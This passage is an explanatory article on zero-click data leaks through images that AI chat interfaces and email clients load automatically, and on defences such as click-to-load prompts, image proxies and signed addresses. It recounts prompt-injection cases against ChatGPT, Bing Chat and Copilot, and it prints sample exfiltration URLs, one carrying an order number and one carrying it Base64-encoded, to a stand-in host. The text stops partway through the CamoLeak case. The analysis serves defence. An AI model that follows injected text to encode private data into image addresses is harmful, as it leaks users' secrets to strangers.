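# Blocking silent network requests from rendered model output

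## What an automatically loaded image tells a server

A chat interface for an AI model, such as ChatGPT or Microsoft Copilot, receives the model's answer as text with formatting marks. A part of the interface called the renderer turns that text into the page the user sees. If the text contains the address of an image, the user's browser will usually fetch the image from the server named in the address while the answer is appearing, before the user clicks anything. Such an image is a kind of remote content, which is anything in a message or page that must be loaded from another server before the reader can see it.

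Senders of bulk email have long put tiny, usually invisible images called tracking pixels in their messages. When a pixel loads, the sender learns that someone opened the message. Email programs and browsers now have controls against these pixels. The privacy problem is worse in a chat interface, because a language model can write a new image address for every answer and put text from the user's email or files in that address. The company that runs the interface can block the request at several points between the model's text and the network, and the best point depends on what triggers the request and what it contains.

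### From Markdown to a network request

Most chat models format their answers in Markdown, which uses punctuation marks for headings, bold type and links. In CommonMark, a widely used Markdown specification, an image is written like a link with an exclamation mark in front: a description in square brackets, then an address in round ones. A shopping assistant might use this to add a picture of a parcel to an answer about a delivery.

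```
![Parcel](https://images.example/parcel.png)
```

(The ending .example leads nowhere; internet standards reserve it for documentation.) The renderer converts the line into HTML, the language of web pages:

```
<img src="https://images.example/parcel.png" alt="Parcel" />
```

An HTML image element holds an address and replacement text, and the browser must fetch the image itself. Under WHATWG's HTML standard, browsers by default do this as soon as the element is created, and again if a script changes the address. A browser may instead let users choose to fetch images on demand, an option the standard mentions for people with little bandwidth. According to MDN's reference page *&lt;img&gt; HTML image embed element*, a page can also mark an image as "lazy", which makes the browser wait until the reader has scrolled near it. That helps little in a chat, because a new answer normally appears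 in the part of the page the user is looking at.

The model only writes the text. The user's browser then contacts the server over the user's own connection, so the request would still happen if the company turned off the model's browsing and every other tool. *Bing Chat*, a 2023 post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog, Embrace The Red, describes the same steps in Microsoft's chatbot of that time. The model returned Markdown, the interface turned it into an image element, and the browser connected to the address without any action by the user.

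The server's reply hardly matters because the information has already left with the request. Browsers must not run scripts inside an image file, and they ignore server error codes when deciding whether an image is valid. The server can return a single transparent pixel or nothing usable. If the image fails to load, visual browsers hide the broken-image icon when the alt text is empty, according to MDN, and empty square brackets in a Markdown image produce empty alt text.

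### What the server's log contains

A web address can end in a query, a question mark followed by named values, which ordinary sites use for search terms and page numbers. Suppose now that the shopping assistant has the customer's order confirmation in front of it, and writes a slightly longer address:

```
https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213
```

The renderer and the browser treat it like the first one. At the other end, most web servers write a line in a log for each request. Apache's *Log Files*, part of the manual for a common web server program, sets out a format in which this invented request would leave the following trace:

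```
203.0.113.7 - - [12/Mar/2026:09:41:07 +0000] "GET /parcel.png?order=48213 HTTP/1.1" 200 5120 "https://chat.example/" "Mozilla/5.0 (Windows NT 10.0; Win64; x64; rv:148.0) Gecko/20100101 Firefox/148.0"
```

| Field | In the example | What the server's owner learns |
|---|---|---|
| IP address | 203.0.113.7 | The internet connection that the request came from |
| Time | 12 March 2026, 09:41:07 | When the answer appeared on the user's screen |
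| Request line | /parcel.png?order=48213 | The full path and query, including the order number |
| Referer | https://chat.example/ | The site whose page contained the image |
| User-Agent | Firefox 148 on Windows | The user's browser and operating system |

The two hyphens stand for login details that the server does not have, and the numbers 200 and 5120 describe its reply. Anyone who can read the log now has the order number, and the owner of images.example did nothing special to collect it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the same risk, explaining that websites commonly log the addresses visitors request and that an address can contain a document title or an email address that the model had access to.

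Some of the other fields are less reliable than they look. The IP address may belong to a proxy, a server that passes on requests for other machines, which hides the user's own address. When the image comes from another site, the Referer (the misspelling is part of the standard) gives only the name of the site the user is on by default, so the server doesn't receive the address of the conversation.

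The image request sometimes also carries cookies, the small pieces of data that a site stores in a browser and gets back with later requests. MDN's *Third-party cookies* explains that the image's server must already have set a cookie in that browser and marked it as usable on other companies' pages. The browser must also allow it. Chrome does so by default outside Incognito mode, while Firefox keeps a separate store of such cookies for each site the user visits, so a server cannot use them to follow the user from one site to another. A server set up for a single attack will rarely have an earlier cookie to collect, but an advertising network may well have one and could then connect the request to a browser it has seen elsewhere.

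The chat page can withhold some of this information. One attribute on the image element stops the browser from sending the Referer header, and another stops it from sending cookies. The browser must still send the image's URL, because the server needs it to find the file.

### Two leaks

Even without the order number, the log line in the example tells the owner of images.example that somebody at 203.0.113.7 had an answer containing the picture on screen at 09:41, and which browser they used. A tracking pixel works the same way. Its address contains nothing the sender didn't already know, but the request for it reveals that someone read the message, and when. A sender who gives each recipient a different address can also tell which of them read it.

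The security company Permiso showed this leak in ChatGPT in May 2026. For *ChatGPhish*, its researchers added instructions to a web page and then asked ChatGPT to summarise it. The answer contained an image from an address they had fixed in advance, and the image loaded every time the answer appeared. Their server received the IP address, the User-Agent, the Referer where the browser supplied one, and precise timing. Permiso considers this enough to confirm that a particular target read a particular page through ChatGPT, which is useful preparation for a further attack. The company first reported the problem to OpenAI under a title that included "Data Exfiltration", which means moving private data out to someone who should not have it, but nothing logged in the image test came from the user's conversation. OpenAI marked the first report as not reproducible and eventually closed a revised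 one as a duplicate of an earlier report.

The second leak occurs when the model reads something private and then includes it in an image address it composes, which the server logs. The order number in the example leaks this way. In Rehberger's demonstration on Bing Chat, an image address likewise carried an encoded summary of the page and the conversation to his server. Hiding the reader's IP address, browser and cookies would not prevent this leak. OpenAI's January 2026 protection, which loads an address automatically only if it was already public, targets composed addresses but can still allow fixed ones.

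### Why a model puts private data into an address

A shopping assistant has no reason of its own to send an order number to a stranger's server, but text it reads can lead it to do so. A model's context is all the text it has when it answers, including the user's question, the conversation so far, and any emails, files or web pages that the interface has retrieved. It can also contain text the user doesn't expect. Rehberger found that ChatGPT placed information from past chats in its system prompt, the standing text that comes before a conversation. He argues in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* that whoever wrote a document the user asks about can therefore get at that information too.

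All of this reaches the model as one sequence of text. Simon Willison, a software developer who has written about the subject since 2022, explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that language models follow instructions in content and cannot reliably tell whose instructions deserve weight. If a web page contains a sentence addressed to AI systems, the model may act on it as though the user had typed it. Placing text in material the model reads so that it follows a stranger's instructions is called prompt injection. Willison named it after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. He distinguishes it from jailbreaking, where the user is trying to get around the model's rules rather than being the victim of the attack.

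Three things have to come together before private data can leave by this route. Willison calls them the lethal trifecta:

- access to private data;
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image an attacker could have influenced;
- a way to send information out.

An attacker can steal private data through an image address only if the model's context contains both the data and a stranger's text asking the model to put it in the address, and the address can leave the user's screen. A tracking pixel works without private data in the context, because it reveals the user's connection and when the image loaded.

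The ability to send data out is generally the easiest of the three conditions to remove. An assistant that reads the user's email already meets the other two, access to private data and exposure to untrusted content, because the mailbox is private and anybody can write to it. Filters that try to recognise injected instructions do not solve the problem. Willison remarks that vendors advertise catching 95% of attacks, which is a failing grade in web security because an attacker can keep trying.

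Models have become better at resisting prompt injection, which is the best argument against worrying so much about how data could leave. In a test commissioned by Anthropic, none of 720 injection attempts, drawn from 72 scenarios, succeeded against three of its 2026 models in its programming tool, Claude Code. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, welcomed the figure in August 2026 but wanted more independent confirmation, and described an attack he doubted the tool could stop. The test also covered programming agents running in a mode that screens their actions, which is quite different from a chat page that loads images automatically. Only a few months earlier, in Permiso's test, ChatGPT had fully followed a web page's instructions about the form of its answer.

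Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers found leaks like this between April 2023 and February 2025, including Google Bard, Slack, GitHub Copilot Chat and xAI's Grok. He writes that almost all the vendors fixed them promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out. GitHub, for example, disabled Markdown images from untrusted domains (Willison, *GitHub Copilot Chat*), but the model could still be fooled.

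### The first report on ChatGPT

*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, by the software engineer Roman Samoilenko, was the first public description of the problem in ChatGPT, which is why ChatGPT is first on Willison's list. Samoilenko tested the version dated 14 March 2023. Willison (2023) drew attention to the report on 14 April in a blog entry of the same title. Rehberger found the same flaw independently. His post, *ChatGPT Plugins*, dates Samoilenko's discovery to the end of March and his own to a few days later.

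Samoilenko's attack put instructions into ChatGPT's context through the user's clipboard, without ChatGPT reading web pages or email. When a visitor copied a passage from a prepared website, a script on the page added instructions to the copied text, which the visitor then pasted into the chat. The instructions were to end the answer with a one-pixel transparent image and to put part of the conversation in the image's address. In one demonstration, the user asked for help with a piece of code, and Samoilenko's server received the corrected code in the image request. In another, the instructions applied to all later answers in the same chat, and the server received each new question as the user asked it.

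He acknowledged that the method was unreliable. The same text could work once and then fail, and success varied with the topic of the conversation, the wording of the user's next message and the position of the instructions in the pasted passage. A slow answer could also alert the user. He found it easy to extract previous questions and code but very difficult to extract passwords and access keys. That difficulty came from the model's behaviour at the time, not from the interface, so it could not be relied on to last. He advised that ChatGPT should not reply with Markdown images. OpenAI began to mitigate the problem in December 2023, according to a later note on Willison's entry. Rehberger reported the problem in Bing Chat to Microsoft on 8 April, and Microsoft had fixed it by 15 June, apparently relying in part on a browser policy that restricts where images may come from.

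### Zero-click and one-click

Samoilenko also tried the attack with an ordinary link instead of an image. The link's address still contained the user's data, but the browser didn't send it until the user clicked. Security researchers call a leak zero-click if it needs no action beyond ordinary use of the product, and one-click if the user has to click a link once. Samoilenko's image attack is zero-click by this definition, even though the user pastes the stranger's text into the chat, because copying and pasting is ordinary use.

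In later cases the attacker no longer needed the clipboard. *EchoLeak*, a case study of a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, describes a zero-click leak that started with one crafted email. Copilot works inside a company's mail and documents, so the attacker only had to send the message. One step in getting the data out was an image that the interface fetched automatically.

*SearchLeak* (Taler, June 2026) described a flaw in the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which treated the search query in a link as instructions to the model. After the victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address, Copilot searched their mailbox and wrote the title of an email into an image address. The browser then requested the image without a second click. Email titles often contain the one-time security codes that websites send to people logging in, the kind of secret that Samoilenko had found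 hard to extract three years earlier. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has fixed it.

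## Email clients that hold images back until the reader asks

The zero-click leaks described so far all depend on a program requesting an image without the user's approval. Many email programs wait for that approval. They display the text of an HTML message but request nothing from other servers. A notice says that some content was not loaded, and the program requests it only if the reader presses a button. Until then, the image's server doesn't receive the reader's IP address, the time of reading or anything written into the image address.

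The block applies only to remote content. *Exploring Content Concealment in Email* (2024) explains that a sender can also attach a picture or write it into the HTML as encoded text. These pictures need no network request, so email programs can show them even when they hold remote images back.

### Current defaults

Classic Outlook, Microsoft's older desktop program, downloads no pictures from the internet until the reader chooses Download Pictures in a bar above the message, according to Microsoft's *Block or unblock automatic picture downloads in classic Outlook email messages*. The reader can also add an address or a whole domain to a list of safe senders, whose pictures then load without a prompt. Microsoft's reasons for the default are tracking pixels, offensive pictures, malicious code and slow connections.

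The newer Windows and web versions of Outlook load images only from safe senders. Microsoft's *Outlook* (2026), a product roadmap notice, kept that default and announced two more settings for July 2026. One blocks all external content, and the other loads all of it if the user's organisation permits. Outlook for Mac holds pictures back too, and Microsoft's *Automatically download pictures from the Internet in Outlook for Mac* describes a middle setting that loads them from the reader's contacts, organisation and safe senders. According to Mozilla, its email program Thunderbird blocks remote content so that the sender gets no information about the reader.

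Gmail also used to hold images back, until Google (2013) announced that it would fetch them through its servers and display them automatically, so that users would no longer have to press "that pesky 'display images below' link". In *Turn images on or off in Gmail*, Google still describes a setting to ask first, but recommends it for slow connections and for saving mobile data. Gmail also holds images back when it classifies a message or its sender as suspicious.

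Proton Mail, an encrypted email service, now also shows remote images automatically because, according to Proton, its tracker protection stops senders from reliably learning who opened a message, when or where. Apple's Mail app has a feature, Protect Mail Activity, that downloads remote content in the background when a message arrives. Users can block all remote content only after they turn that feature off.

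| Program | Remote images by default | What the reader can choose |
|---|---|---|
| Classic Outlook | Holds them back | Load for one message, a sender, a domain or everyone |
| New Outlook for Windows and the web | Loads them from safe senders | Block everything, or load everything if the organisation permits (announced for July 2026) |
| Outlook for Mac | Holds them back | Always load, load from known senders, or ask |
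| Thunderbird | Holds them back | Load for one message, a website, a sender or everyone |
| Apple Mail with Protect Mail Activity on | Downloads them when the message arrives | Turn the feature off, then select Block All Remote Content |
| Proton Mail | Loads them | Load manually, with a separate setting in each app |
| Gmail | Loads them unless the message looks suspicious | Ask before displaying external images |

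Email clients that now load images automatically can hide the reader from the sender, generally by fetching the images through a company's servers. This conceals most of what a tracking pixel would reveal, but not data written into the image's address.

An email client that blocks images in one view may load them in another. Outlook's phone app has a Block External Images setting, but Microsoft's *What is Block External Images in my settings?* notes that it covers only the reading pane. External images load normally when the user replies to the message. A chat interface could have the same gap if it blocks images in a live conversation but loads them when the user reopens it from the history or views a shared copy.

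### Permission for a sender

Clicking to load images in every message is tedious, so most of these programs let the reader approve a sender once. This approach depends on the program correctly identifying who sent the message. An older version of Mozilla's *Remote Content in Messages* warns that senders' addresses are easy to forge, and that it is much harder to impersonate the website that stores the images. Thunderbird therefore lets the reader approve a website as well as a sender.

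Gmail dealt with forged addresses differently, by showing images by default only in messages that had passed SPF or DKIM, two checks that a message really comes from the domain it names (Google, 2009). An image from one of the reader's own contacts could therefore stay hidden if the contact's mail service didn't support those checks.

A rule that allows remote content from a sender also covers whatever that sender includes in future. On Mozilla's support forum, a Thunderbird user named johannes gave the example of a newsletter that later adds trackers from social networks or Amazon, which would then load without a prompt. The sender can also replace the image at a web address the reader has already seen, or show different images to different visitors.

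### What email images were found to reveal

The most detailed measurement of these requests predates Apple's and Proton's present protections. It comes from *I never signed up for this!* (Englehardt, Han and Narayanan, 2018), a study of commercial mailing lists. The researchers' software visited 15,700 websites, filled in the sign-up forms it found with email addresses created for the purpose, and collected 12,618 emails from 902 senders. The researchers then opened each email twice in a simulated webmail program that ran no scripts but loaded all other content, and recorded the requests.

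About 85% of the emails loaded something from a third party (a company other than the sender), and 70% contained items that common blocklists class as trackers. About 29% gave the recipient's email address to at least one third party. The researchers counted 100,963 such leaks and judged 62% of them intentional, mostly because the sender had put the recipient's address in the image's URL.

This is closer to the chat problem than an ordinary tracking pixel is, because the request contains personal data. In email, though, the sender already knew the data and was passing it to a business partner, whereas a stranger who injects instructions into a chat doesn't know what is in the user's mailbox and uses the image request to find out.

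The study also shows how hard it is to see what a web address contains. Many senders included a hash of the email address instead of the email address itself. A hash is a fixed-length string that looks random to a person, but a company can match it by hashing the email addresses it already holds. To find these hashes, the researchers' software tried 24 hash functions and ten other encodings, in up to three layers.

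The address also doesn't show readers everyone who will receive a request if they approve an image. One tracking pixel in a newsletter from the *Washington Examiner* started a chain of 13 requests, in which each server redirected the browser to another address, several of them belonging to different advertising companies. When the researchers opened the emails a second time, about 21% loaded something that hadn't loaded the first time.

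Researchers tested 16 email programs by hand and found that five blocked images by default and another eight did so only for suspected spam. Two widely used blocklists would also have cut the number of third parties receiving email addresses from 99 to 51. Blocklists work against advertisers because the same companies appear in thousands of messages, but they would do little against a server that an attacker had just set up to receive data from a chat interface.

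The figures don't describe an ordinary mailbox, because the sample contained only mailing lists and no spam, and Englehardt and colleagues assumed an email program with few restrictions. Another 2018 study, *Privacy Risk Assessment on Email Tracking*, used more than 44,000 emails from a seven-year period, evaluated existing defences and proposed guidelines for more comprehensive ones. More recently, *Exploring Content Concealment in Email* set aside 1,260,292 emails because they used remote content and kept 2,039,409 that did not. About 38% therefore used remote content, but the study was about attackers' emails and didn't count trackers, so it can't show whether tracking has fallen since 2018.

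### EFAIL

In 2018 researchers in Germany and Belgium used remote images to read encrypted email. Their attacks, called EFAIL, targeted OpenPGP and S/MIME, the two main standards for end-to-end email encryption. Only the sender and recipients hold the keys, so a copy stolen from a mail server should be useless. An EFAIL attacker alters a stolen copy and sends it to someone who can decrypt it. That person's email program decrypts the text and sends it to the attacker in a request for a remote image.

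The EFAIL researchers' website describes two methods. The simpler one, direct exfiltration, wraps the encrypted text in ordinary HTML so that it falls inside an unfinished image address. A vulnerable program decrypts the text and joins the parts into one page, which makes the decrypted message part of the address. When the program requests the image, the message ends up in the attacker's server log. Apple Mail, the iPhone's Mail app and Thunderbird had this flaw.

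The other method exploits the encryption. OpenPGP and S/MIME used forms of encryption that let an attacker who knows a small piece of a message change the encrypted copy so that this piece decrypts to something else. Emails begin with predictable lines, so the attacker usually knows enough to insert an image element whose address includes the rest of the text. OpenPGP had a check that could detect such changes, but when it failed, several programs warned the user and displayed the altered message anyway. The program could therefore request the image before the user read the warning.

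In *Efail*, Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues (2018) found ways to extract text from 23 of the 35 S/MIME programs they tested and 10 of the 28 OpenPGP programs. Some of these leaked only if the user clicked a link or chose to load external images.

Poddebniak and colleagues reported in a May 2018 draft that 13 of 48 email programs loaded external images by default, while the others blocked them or asked first. The researchers then tried a long list of HTML elements and attributes that can hold a web address, and got past the blocks in 22 programs. Style sheets, which control the look of a page and can also load images, got past them in 11. In three programs, encrypting the message was enough. A chat interface that blocks only the Markdown image syntax is open to the same kind of bypass if its renderer accepts other elements that fetch remote content.

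Where the block worked, it turned a zero-click leak into a one-click leak, in the terms used for chat interfaces. Apple's two mail programs loaded images by default, so direct exfiltration required only that the reader open the message. Because Thunderbird held images back, the researchers had to disguise the message so that a click anywhere in it would submit the text.

The makers of the affected programs released fixes, but other researchers soon published ways around those in Thunderbird and Apple Mail. The standards changed more slowly. The new OpenPGP draft followed the EFAIL researchers' recommendation that programs not display altered messages. The S/MIME draft recommended a form of encryption that detects changes, and warned programs to treat the parts of a mixed message as if they came from different sources. Five years later, Ising, Poddebniak and colleagues (2023) reported in *Content-Type*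 that S/MIME 4.0 recommends the safer encryption but still requires programs to support an older kind. They also found that Google's hosted S/MIME service marks unsigned messages as suspicious, as a stopgap against EFAIL. This turns off automatic images, so Google again asks readers before loading images in these messages, long after it dropped the prompt for most other mail.

Email clients that block images can still leak data in other ways. *Re: What's Up Johnny?* (Müller, Brinkmann and colleagues, 2019) describes attacks in which a victim who replied to a harmless-looking email could unknowingly send the attacker the decrypted text of other emails. Of the clients tested, 17 of 19 that supported OpenPGP and 21 of 22 that supported S/MIME were vulnerable to at least one of the paper's attacks.

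Poddebniak and colleagues regarded blocking network requests as a short-term measure, because the underlying flaw was in the encryption standards and new standards could fix it. Prompt injection has no equivalent fix, because a language model cannot reliably tell a stranger's instructions from its user's. Chat interfaces therefore have to rely more heavily on blocking requests, and for longer.

### "Load this image?" in a chat

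A chat interface could copy Thunderbird's approach. When the model writes a Markdown image, the renderer would keep the address as plain text and show a box with a button instead of the image. It would create the HTML image element, which makes the browser contact the server, only when the user pressed the button. The interface's own pictures, such as charts drawn by the company's servers, would appear as before, as attached pictures do in email.

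Holding an image back until the reader asks for it makes it about as risky as an ordinary link. This would have stopped the automatic image requests in Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT and Rehberger's on Bing Chat, and Permiso's tracking image would not have loaded when the summary appeared. In SearchLeak, the victim had already clicked a link to Microsoft's site, but the email title would have stayed in the browser until they clicked again.

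Someone reading an email knows, or thinks they know, who sent it, and has to decide whether that sender may learn that they opened it. If they decide wrongly, the sender usually learns an IP address and a time. Microsoft's help page for the Outlook phone app even says that external images "are not a security threat". That is nearly right for ordinary email, since the sender fixed the image addresses before sending the message. The decision is harder in a chat, because the model composes the address after reading the user's files, and a stranger may have told it what to include.

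Permission for a sender makes no sense in a chat, because every answer comes from the same assistant and approving it once would switch the protection off. Permission for a website has a clearer meaning but is riskier than in Thunderbird, because the model could then send an approved site any text in the context, in any later answer. Gmail's 2009 solution doesn't carry over either. SPF and DKIM can confirm which domain sent an email, but no comparable check establishes whose text led the model to write a particular address.

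The main argument against a placeholder is that people learn to click through prompts. After seeing the box many times with nothing wrong, they stop reading it and press the button even when the image is harmful. Email's history gives this some support. Mozilla conceded in an older help page that clicking for each message "can get annoying", and Google presented the end of its own prompt as a benefit to users. Neither example measures how often people approve a harmful image, but both suggest that companies will face pressure to remove the button or add an "always allow" option.

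One reply is to show the full address, so that the user can see what the button will send. That works if the address ends in something like "order=48213". It works much less well if the model has encoded the same text:

```
https://images.example/b3JkZXI9NDgyMTM/parcel.png
```

The string in the middle is "order=48213" in Base64, a common way of writing data with letters and digits. Many harmless image addresses contain similar strings, and the researchers who studied mailing lists needed software to pick out the email addresses. A one-time login code is even harder to spot, since six digits make a normal file name. Showing the image address will help a careful user notice an unfamiliar website, but it can't assure them that the rest of the address is harmless or show where the server may redirect the browser.

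The box can at least describe the risk plainly. "Load external image?" sounds like a question about bandwidth or taste, whereas "This address may contain information from your conversation" tells the user why loading the image could be harmful. The interface must supply this wording, not the model, because injected instructions can control the model's text, including the image's description. They can also make the rest of the answer refer to a chart that the user "needs" to load. EFAIL describes a similar trick in Thunderbird, where a message was disguised to get the user to click.

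The other option is to limit each approval to one image at one address, so the reader would have no way to approve all the images in an answer or conversation at once. Apple Mail on the iPhone has a single button that loads every image in a message, according to Grepular's *Apple's "Protect Mail Activity" Doesn't Work*. That is reasonable when one sender chose all the images, but in a chat answer, nine of ten images might come from a shop's catalogue and the tenth from an attacker.

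Frequent requests to approve individual images would worsen prompt fatigue, so the interface has to ask rarely. It can show its own images without asking and use other controls to approve addresses it can confirm are safe. OpenAI does something similar for links in ChatGPT, warning the user before the browser opens an address that it could not verify as public.

A placeholder also has an advantage over the security warnings that people are used to dismissing. A website warning blocks the page the user wants, which gives them a reason to dismiss it. An image in a chat answer is usually an extra, so a user can ignore the placeholder and still read the text. The image then never loads, and no data leaks through it. The exception is people who ask a chatbot for pictures, for example to compare shoes or identify a plant, and they would also see the placeholder most often.

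Whether a load button offers enough protection depends on what the model has read. In a general chat about public matters, it is reasonable to let the reader load an unknown image with a click, since a mistake will usually reveal little more than a tracking pixel does. If the assistant has access to a company's mailbox, a single wrong click can send out a login code or the title of a confidential email. In that case it is safer to offer no button for addresses that no other check has cleared, or to leave images out altogether, as ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode does.

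## Loading images through a proxy

Gmail now loads images through a proxy, a server that requests remote images for the reader and passes them on, so the image's host has no contact with the reader's device. Apple and GitHub have also built proxies, each with a different design. All three hide the reader fairly well, but an ordinary proxy sends the image's address to the host unchanged, including any private text in it.

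### Gmail's proxy

When Gmail displays a message, it replaces each image address with one on a Google domain. The reader's browser requests the image from Google, and Google's server requests the original from the sender's host, converts it and returns the copy. *Images Now Showing* (Rae-Grant, 2013), by Gmail's product manager, presented this as a security measure because Google would also check the images for known viruses and malware.

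In the week of the launch, Filippo Valsorda tested what the sender's server receives (*How the new Gmail image proxy works*, 2013). He emailed himself a message containing an image hosted on his own server, which recorded the details of every request. No request came when the message reached his phone or when he opened his inbox on a computer. When he opened the message, a request arrived at once from a Google address. It contained no cookies and described the browser as Firefox on Windows, although he was using Chrome on a Mac. Valsorda welcomed this but pointed out that the sender still learned the most useful fact, that he had opened the email and when.

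The host gets no cookies because the browser connects to Google instead. This breaks some images that companies keep on internal servers and show only to logged-in users. Google lets a company's administrators exempt trusted internal addresses from the proxy, but advises them to consult their security team first.

Google also keeps copies of images, which can hide repeat openings from the sender, though early accounts differ on how often. Valsorda saw a new request every time he downloaded the image. Litmus, which sells email tracking tools, reported that opening an email again in the same browser usually didn't send a request to its servers, while opening it in the Gmail phone app counted separately. If all recipients get the same image address, the sender may see only the first opening by anyone. Litmus therefore told its customers to give each recipient a different address, which kept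 the tracking working.

Such a URL can even contain the recipient's email address, as in an example from odd.blog's *Privacy* (2013). When Google fetches the image, the sender learns that this person's mailbox is in use. In its help text at the time, Google acknowledged that "unique image links" could reveal that a message had been opened, and it still tells users that senders may sometimes know.

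The time of the request is now a little less reliable as a sign of when the user opened the message than it was in Valsorda's test. MessageBird's *Update on the Gmail App Prefetching Images* (2022) reports that Gmail sometimes fetches images just before it displays a new message, if the user already has Gmail open. This inflated MessageBird's count of opened emails only marginally.

| Information | What the image's host learns through Gmail |
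|---|---|
| IP address | Google's, not the reader's |
| Time of reading | Usually the time of the first opening |
| Cookies | None |
| The image's address | All of it, including any part that identifies the recipient |

### Apple's two relays

Apple's Mail Privacy Protection, introduced in 2021, is mainly meant to hide when a message is read. Its Protect Mail Activity setting downloads images in the background whether or not the user opens the message, according to Apple's *Mail Privacy Protection & Privacy*. The host still receives a request for each image, but the request is no longer evidence that anyone read the message. Bruce Schneier (2022), in *Apple Mail Now Blocks Email Trackers*, notes that in practice every message delivered to Apple Mail now appears to have been read.

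The download passes through two relays, which are proxies run by different organisations. The first relay can see the user's IP address but not the content. It passes the request to the second, which can see the content but not the IP address and gives the host only a generalised identity. Neither organisation can therefore connect a particular person with a particular email. Gmail's design doesn't have this separation, because Google runs both the proxy and the mailbox.

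The protection depends on which program the user reads the mail in. Twilio SendGrid's *Understanding Apple Mail Privacy Protection and Open Events* explains that if someone who receives a message in Apple Mail also opens it in Gmail's web app, the sender gets an ordinary record of that opening. SendGrid, which delivers bulk email, marks openings it suspects Apple's software caused so that its customers can discount them.

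Mike Cardwell, who writes Grepular, found that the background download didn't happen when he tested the Mail app on two iPhones. He waited for hours after messages arrived, but the phones fetched the images only when he opened the messages. The requests did go through Apple's relays, which hid his IP address. He also found that one kind of HTML element made the phone look up the sender's domain name as soon as the message appeared in the inbox list, which revealed to the sender that it had arrived. Apple closed his report, saying that the feature worked as expected. Cardwell suspected that his type of mail account or his being in the UK might explain the result, so it may not apply to most users.

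When Mail can't download content privately, for example because the user has a VPN, it doesn't load the content unless the user taps Load Content, according to Apple's *If you see 'Unable to load remote content privately'*. The request to load it then bypasses the relays.

| Information | What the image's host learns through Apple's relays |
|---|---|
| IP address | A relay's, not the reader's |
| Time of reading | Nothing reliable, if the background download works as Apple describes |
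| Cookies | Apple's description doesn't mention them |
| The image's address | All of it, including any part that identifies the recipient |

### Camo's signed addresses

GitHub lets users put images from other websites in comments and project READMEs. It wrote a proxy called Camo to avoid the warnings browsers show when a secure page loads an image over an insecure connection. GitHub later also sent images that already used secure connections through Camo, so that other companies would not receive its users' browser details (GitHub's *Proxying User Images*).

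Camo fetches an image only if GitHub has signed its address. Go-Camo, another program built on the same design, sets out the process in order:

1. Somebody posts a comment with an image from another site, and the website finds the image's address in the text.
2. The website calculates a signature from the address and a secret key.
3. It replaces the original address with one on the proxy's domain, which contains the signature and an encoded copy of the original.
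4. A reader's browser requests the new address from the proxy.
5. The proxy checks the signature against the encoded address. If they match, it fetches the image and passes it on. If they don't, it refuses.

On GitHub the finished address has this form:

```
https://camo.githubusercontent.com/<signature>/<encoded original address>
```

The signature is an HMAC, a kind of hash that also depends on a secret key. Anyone can calculate an ordinary hash of a web address, but only a server with the key can calculate its HMAC. Changing one character of the address invalidates the signature. According to GitHub's *camo*, the signature has 40 hexadecimal digits, so there are 16⁴⁰ (about 1.5 × 10⁴⁸) possible values.

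The proxy also refuses files that are too large or not of an approved image type. It keeps copies of images, but GitHub tells owners of images that change often to mark them "no-cache" so that Camo won't show old versions. An owner who does this can receive a request each time someone views the page. The requests don't identify the viewers, because everyone who reads a public comment gets the same signed address.

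| Information | What the image's host learns through Camo |
|---|---|
| IP address | GitHub's, not the reader's |
| Time of reading | That somebody viewed the page, unless Camo already has a copy |
| Cookies | None from the reader's browser |
| The image's address | All of it |

### A plain proxy in a chat interface

Suppose the company behind the shopping assistant adopts a proxy like Gmail's. The model writes an image address containing the customer's order number, the interface replaces it with an address on the company's domain, and the company's server fetches the image. The log at images.example now has this line:

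```
198.51.100.24 - - [12/Mar/2026:09:41:07 +0000] "GET /parcel.png?order=48213 HTTP/1.1" 200 5120 "-" "ImageProxy/1.0"
```

The proxy's request for the image doesn't include the customer's IP address, browser or chat site. It still includes the order number, because the proxy needs the full URL to fetch the image. The company could have the proxy remove everything after the question mark, but the model could put the number in the file name instead.

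Storing copies of images doesn't help either. A stored copy prevents a request only if someone has already loaded the same address, and an address the model has just written to include a user's private data is almost always new.

Apple's early download would make things worse in a chat. It works in email because the sender sets the image's URL before the message arrives, so the download only has to hide when the reader opens it. In a chat, the URL may contain the user's data, and downloading the image in the background would send that data even if the user closed the page before reaching that part of the answer. Two relays would hide the user's IP address, but an email address or account number in the URL can still identify the user.

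GitHub (2017) reported this weakness in another company's proxy. Gravatar, which supplies profile pictures to other websites, lets a site name a substitute image for people who have no picture, and it fetched that substitute through its own proxy. Testers from the security firm Cure53 showed that an attacker could use this feature to send text from a GitHub page to an outside server. Chat interfaces have had the same problem more recently. Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* includes a flaw that Microsoft patched in November 2026. The assistant put confidential information in an image address, and Microsoft's search engine Bing passed it on by fetching the image.

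A plain proxy protects against tracking pixels. In Permiso's test on ChatGPT, where the image address was fixed in advance, a proxy would have hidden the user's IP address, browser and Referer. Permiso would still have learned when ChatGPT displayed the summary, at least the first time. Chat companies therefore have a good reason to run a proxy, but they need another defense to stop a model from sending out what it has read.

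### Why signatures help

The signature check lets the proxy block a request that carries the order number. The model can write an address in Camo's format, but without the key it can't work out the signature for an address ending in "order=48213" and would have to guess all 40 digits. The attacker can't supply the signature in the injected instructions, because they would need to know the order number first.

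GitHub made this argument in 2017 about an attack that, like EFAIL's direct exfiltration, used an unfinished image address. The attacker inserted HTML into a page to capture secrets. GitHub reasoned that an attacker who didn't know the secrets beforehand could never obtain a valid signature for the full address containing them.

The argument holds only if the interface doesn't sign whatever the model writes. GitHub automatically signs the addresses of outside images in a README when a user saves the file. If a chat interface did the same with the model's answer, it would sign the address containing the order number, and the proxy would fetch it. Copilot Chat, GitHub's assistant for questions about code, didn't do this, so an attacker needed signatures made in advance.

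### CamoLeak

In June 2025 Omer Mayraz, a researcher at Legit Security, found a way to leak private data through Camo without forging a signature. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how he started with a pull request, which is a proposal to change a project's code. On GitHub, the description of a pull request can contain comments that other users don't see on the page, but Copilot Chat read them as part of its context. When Mayraz logged in as a different user and opened the pull request, the instructions he had hidden in a comment also affected that user's Copilot.

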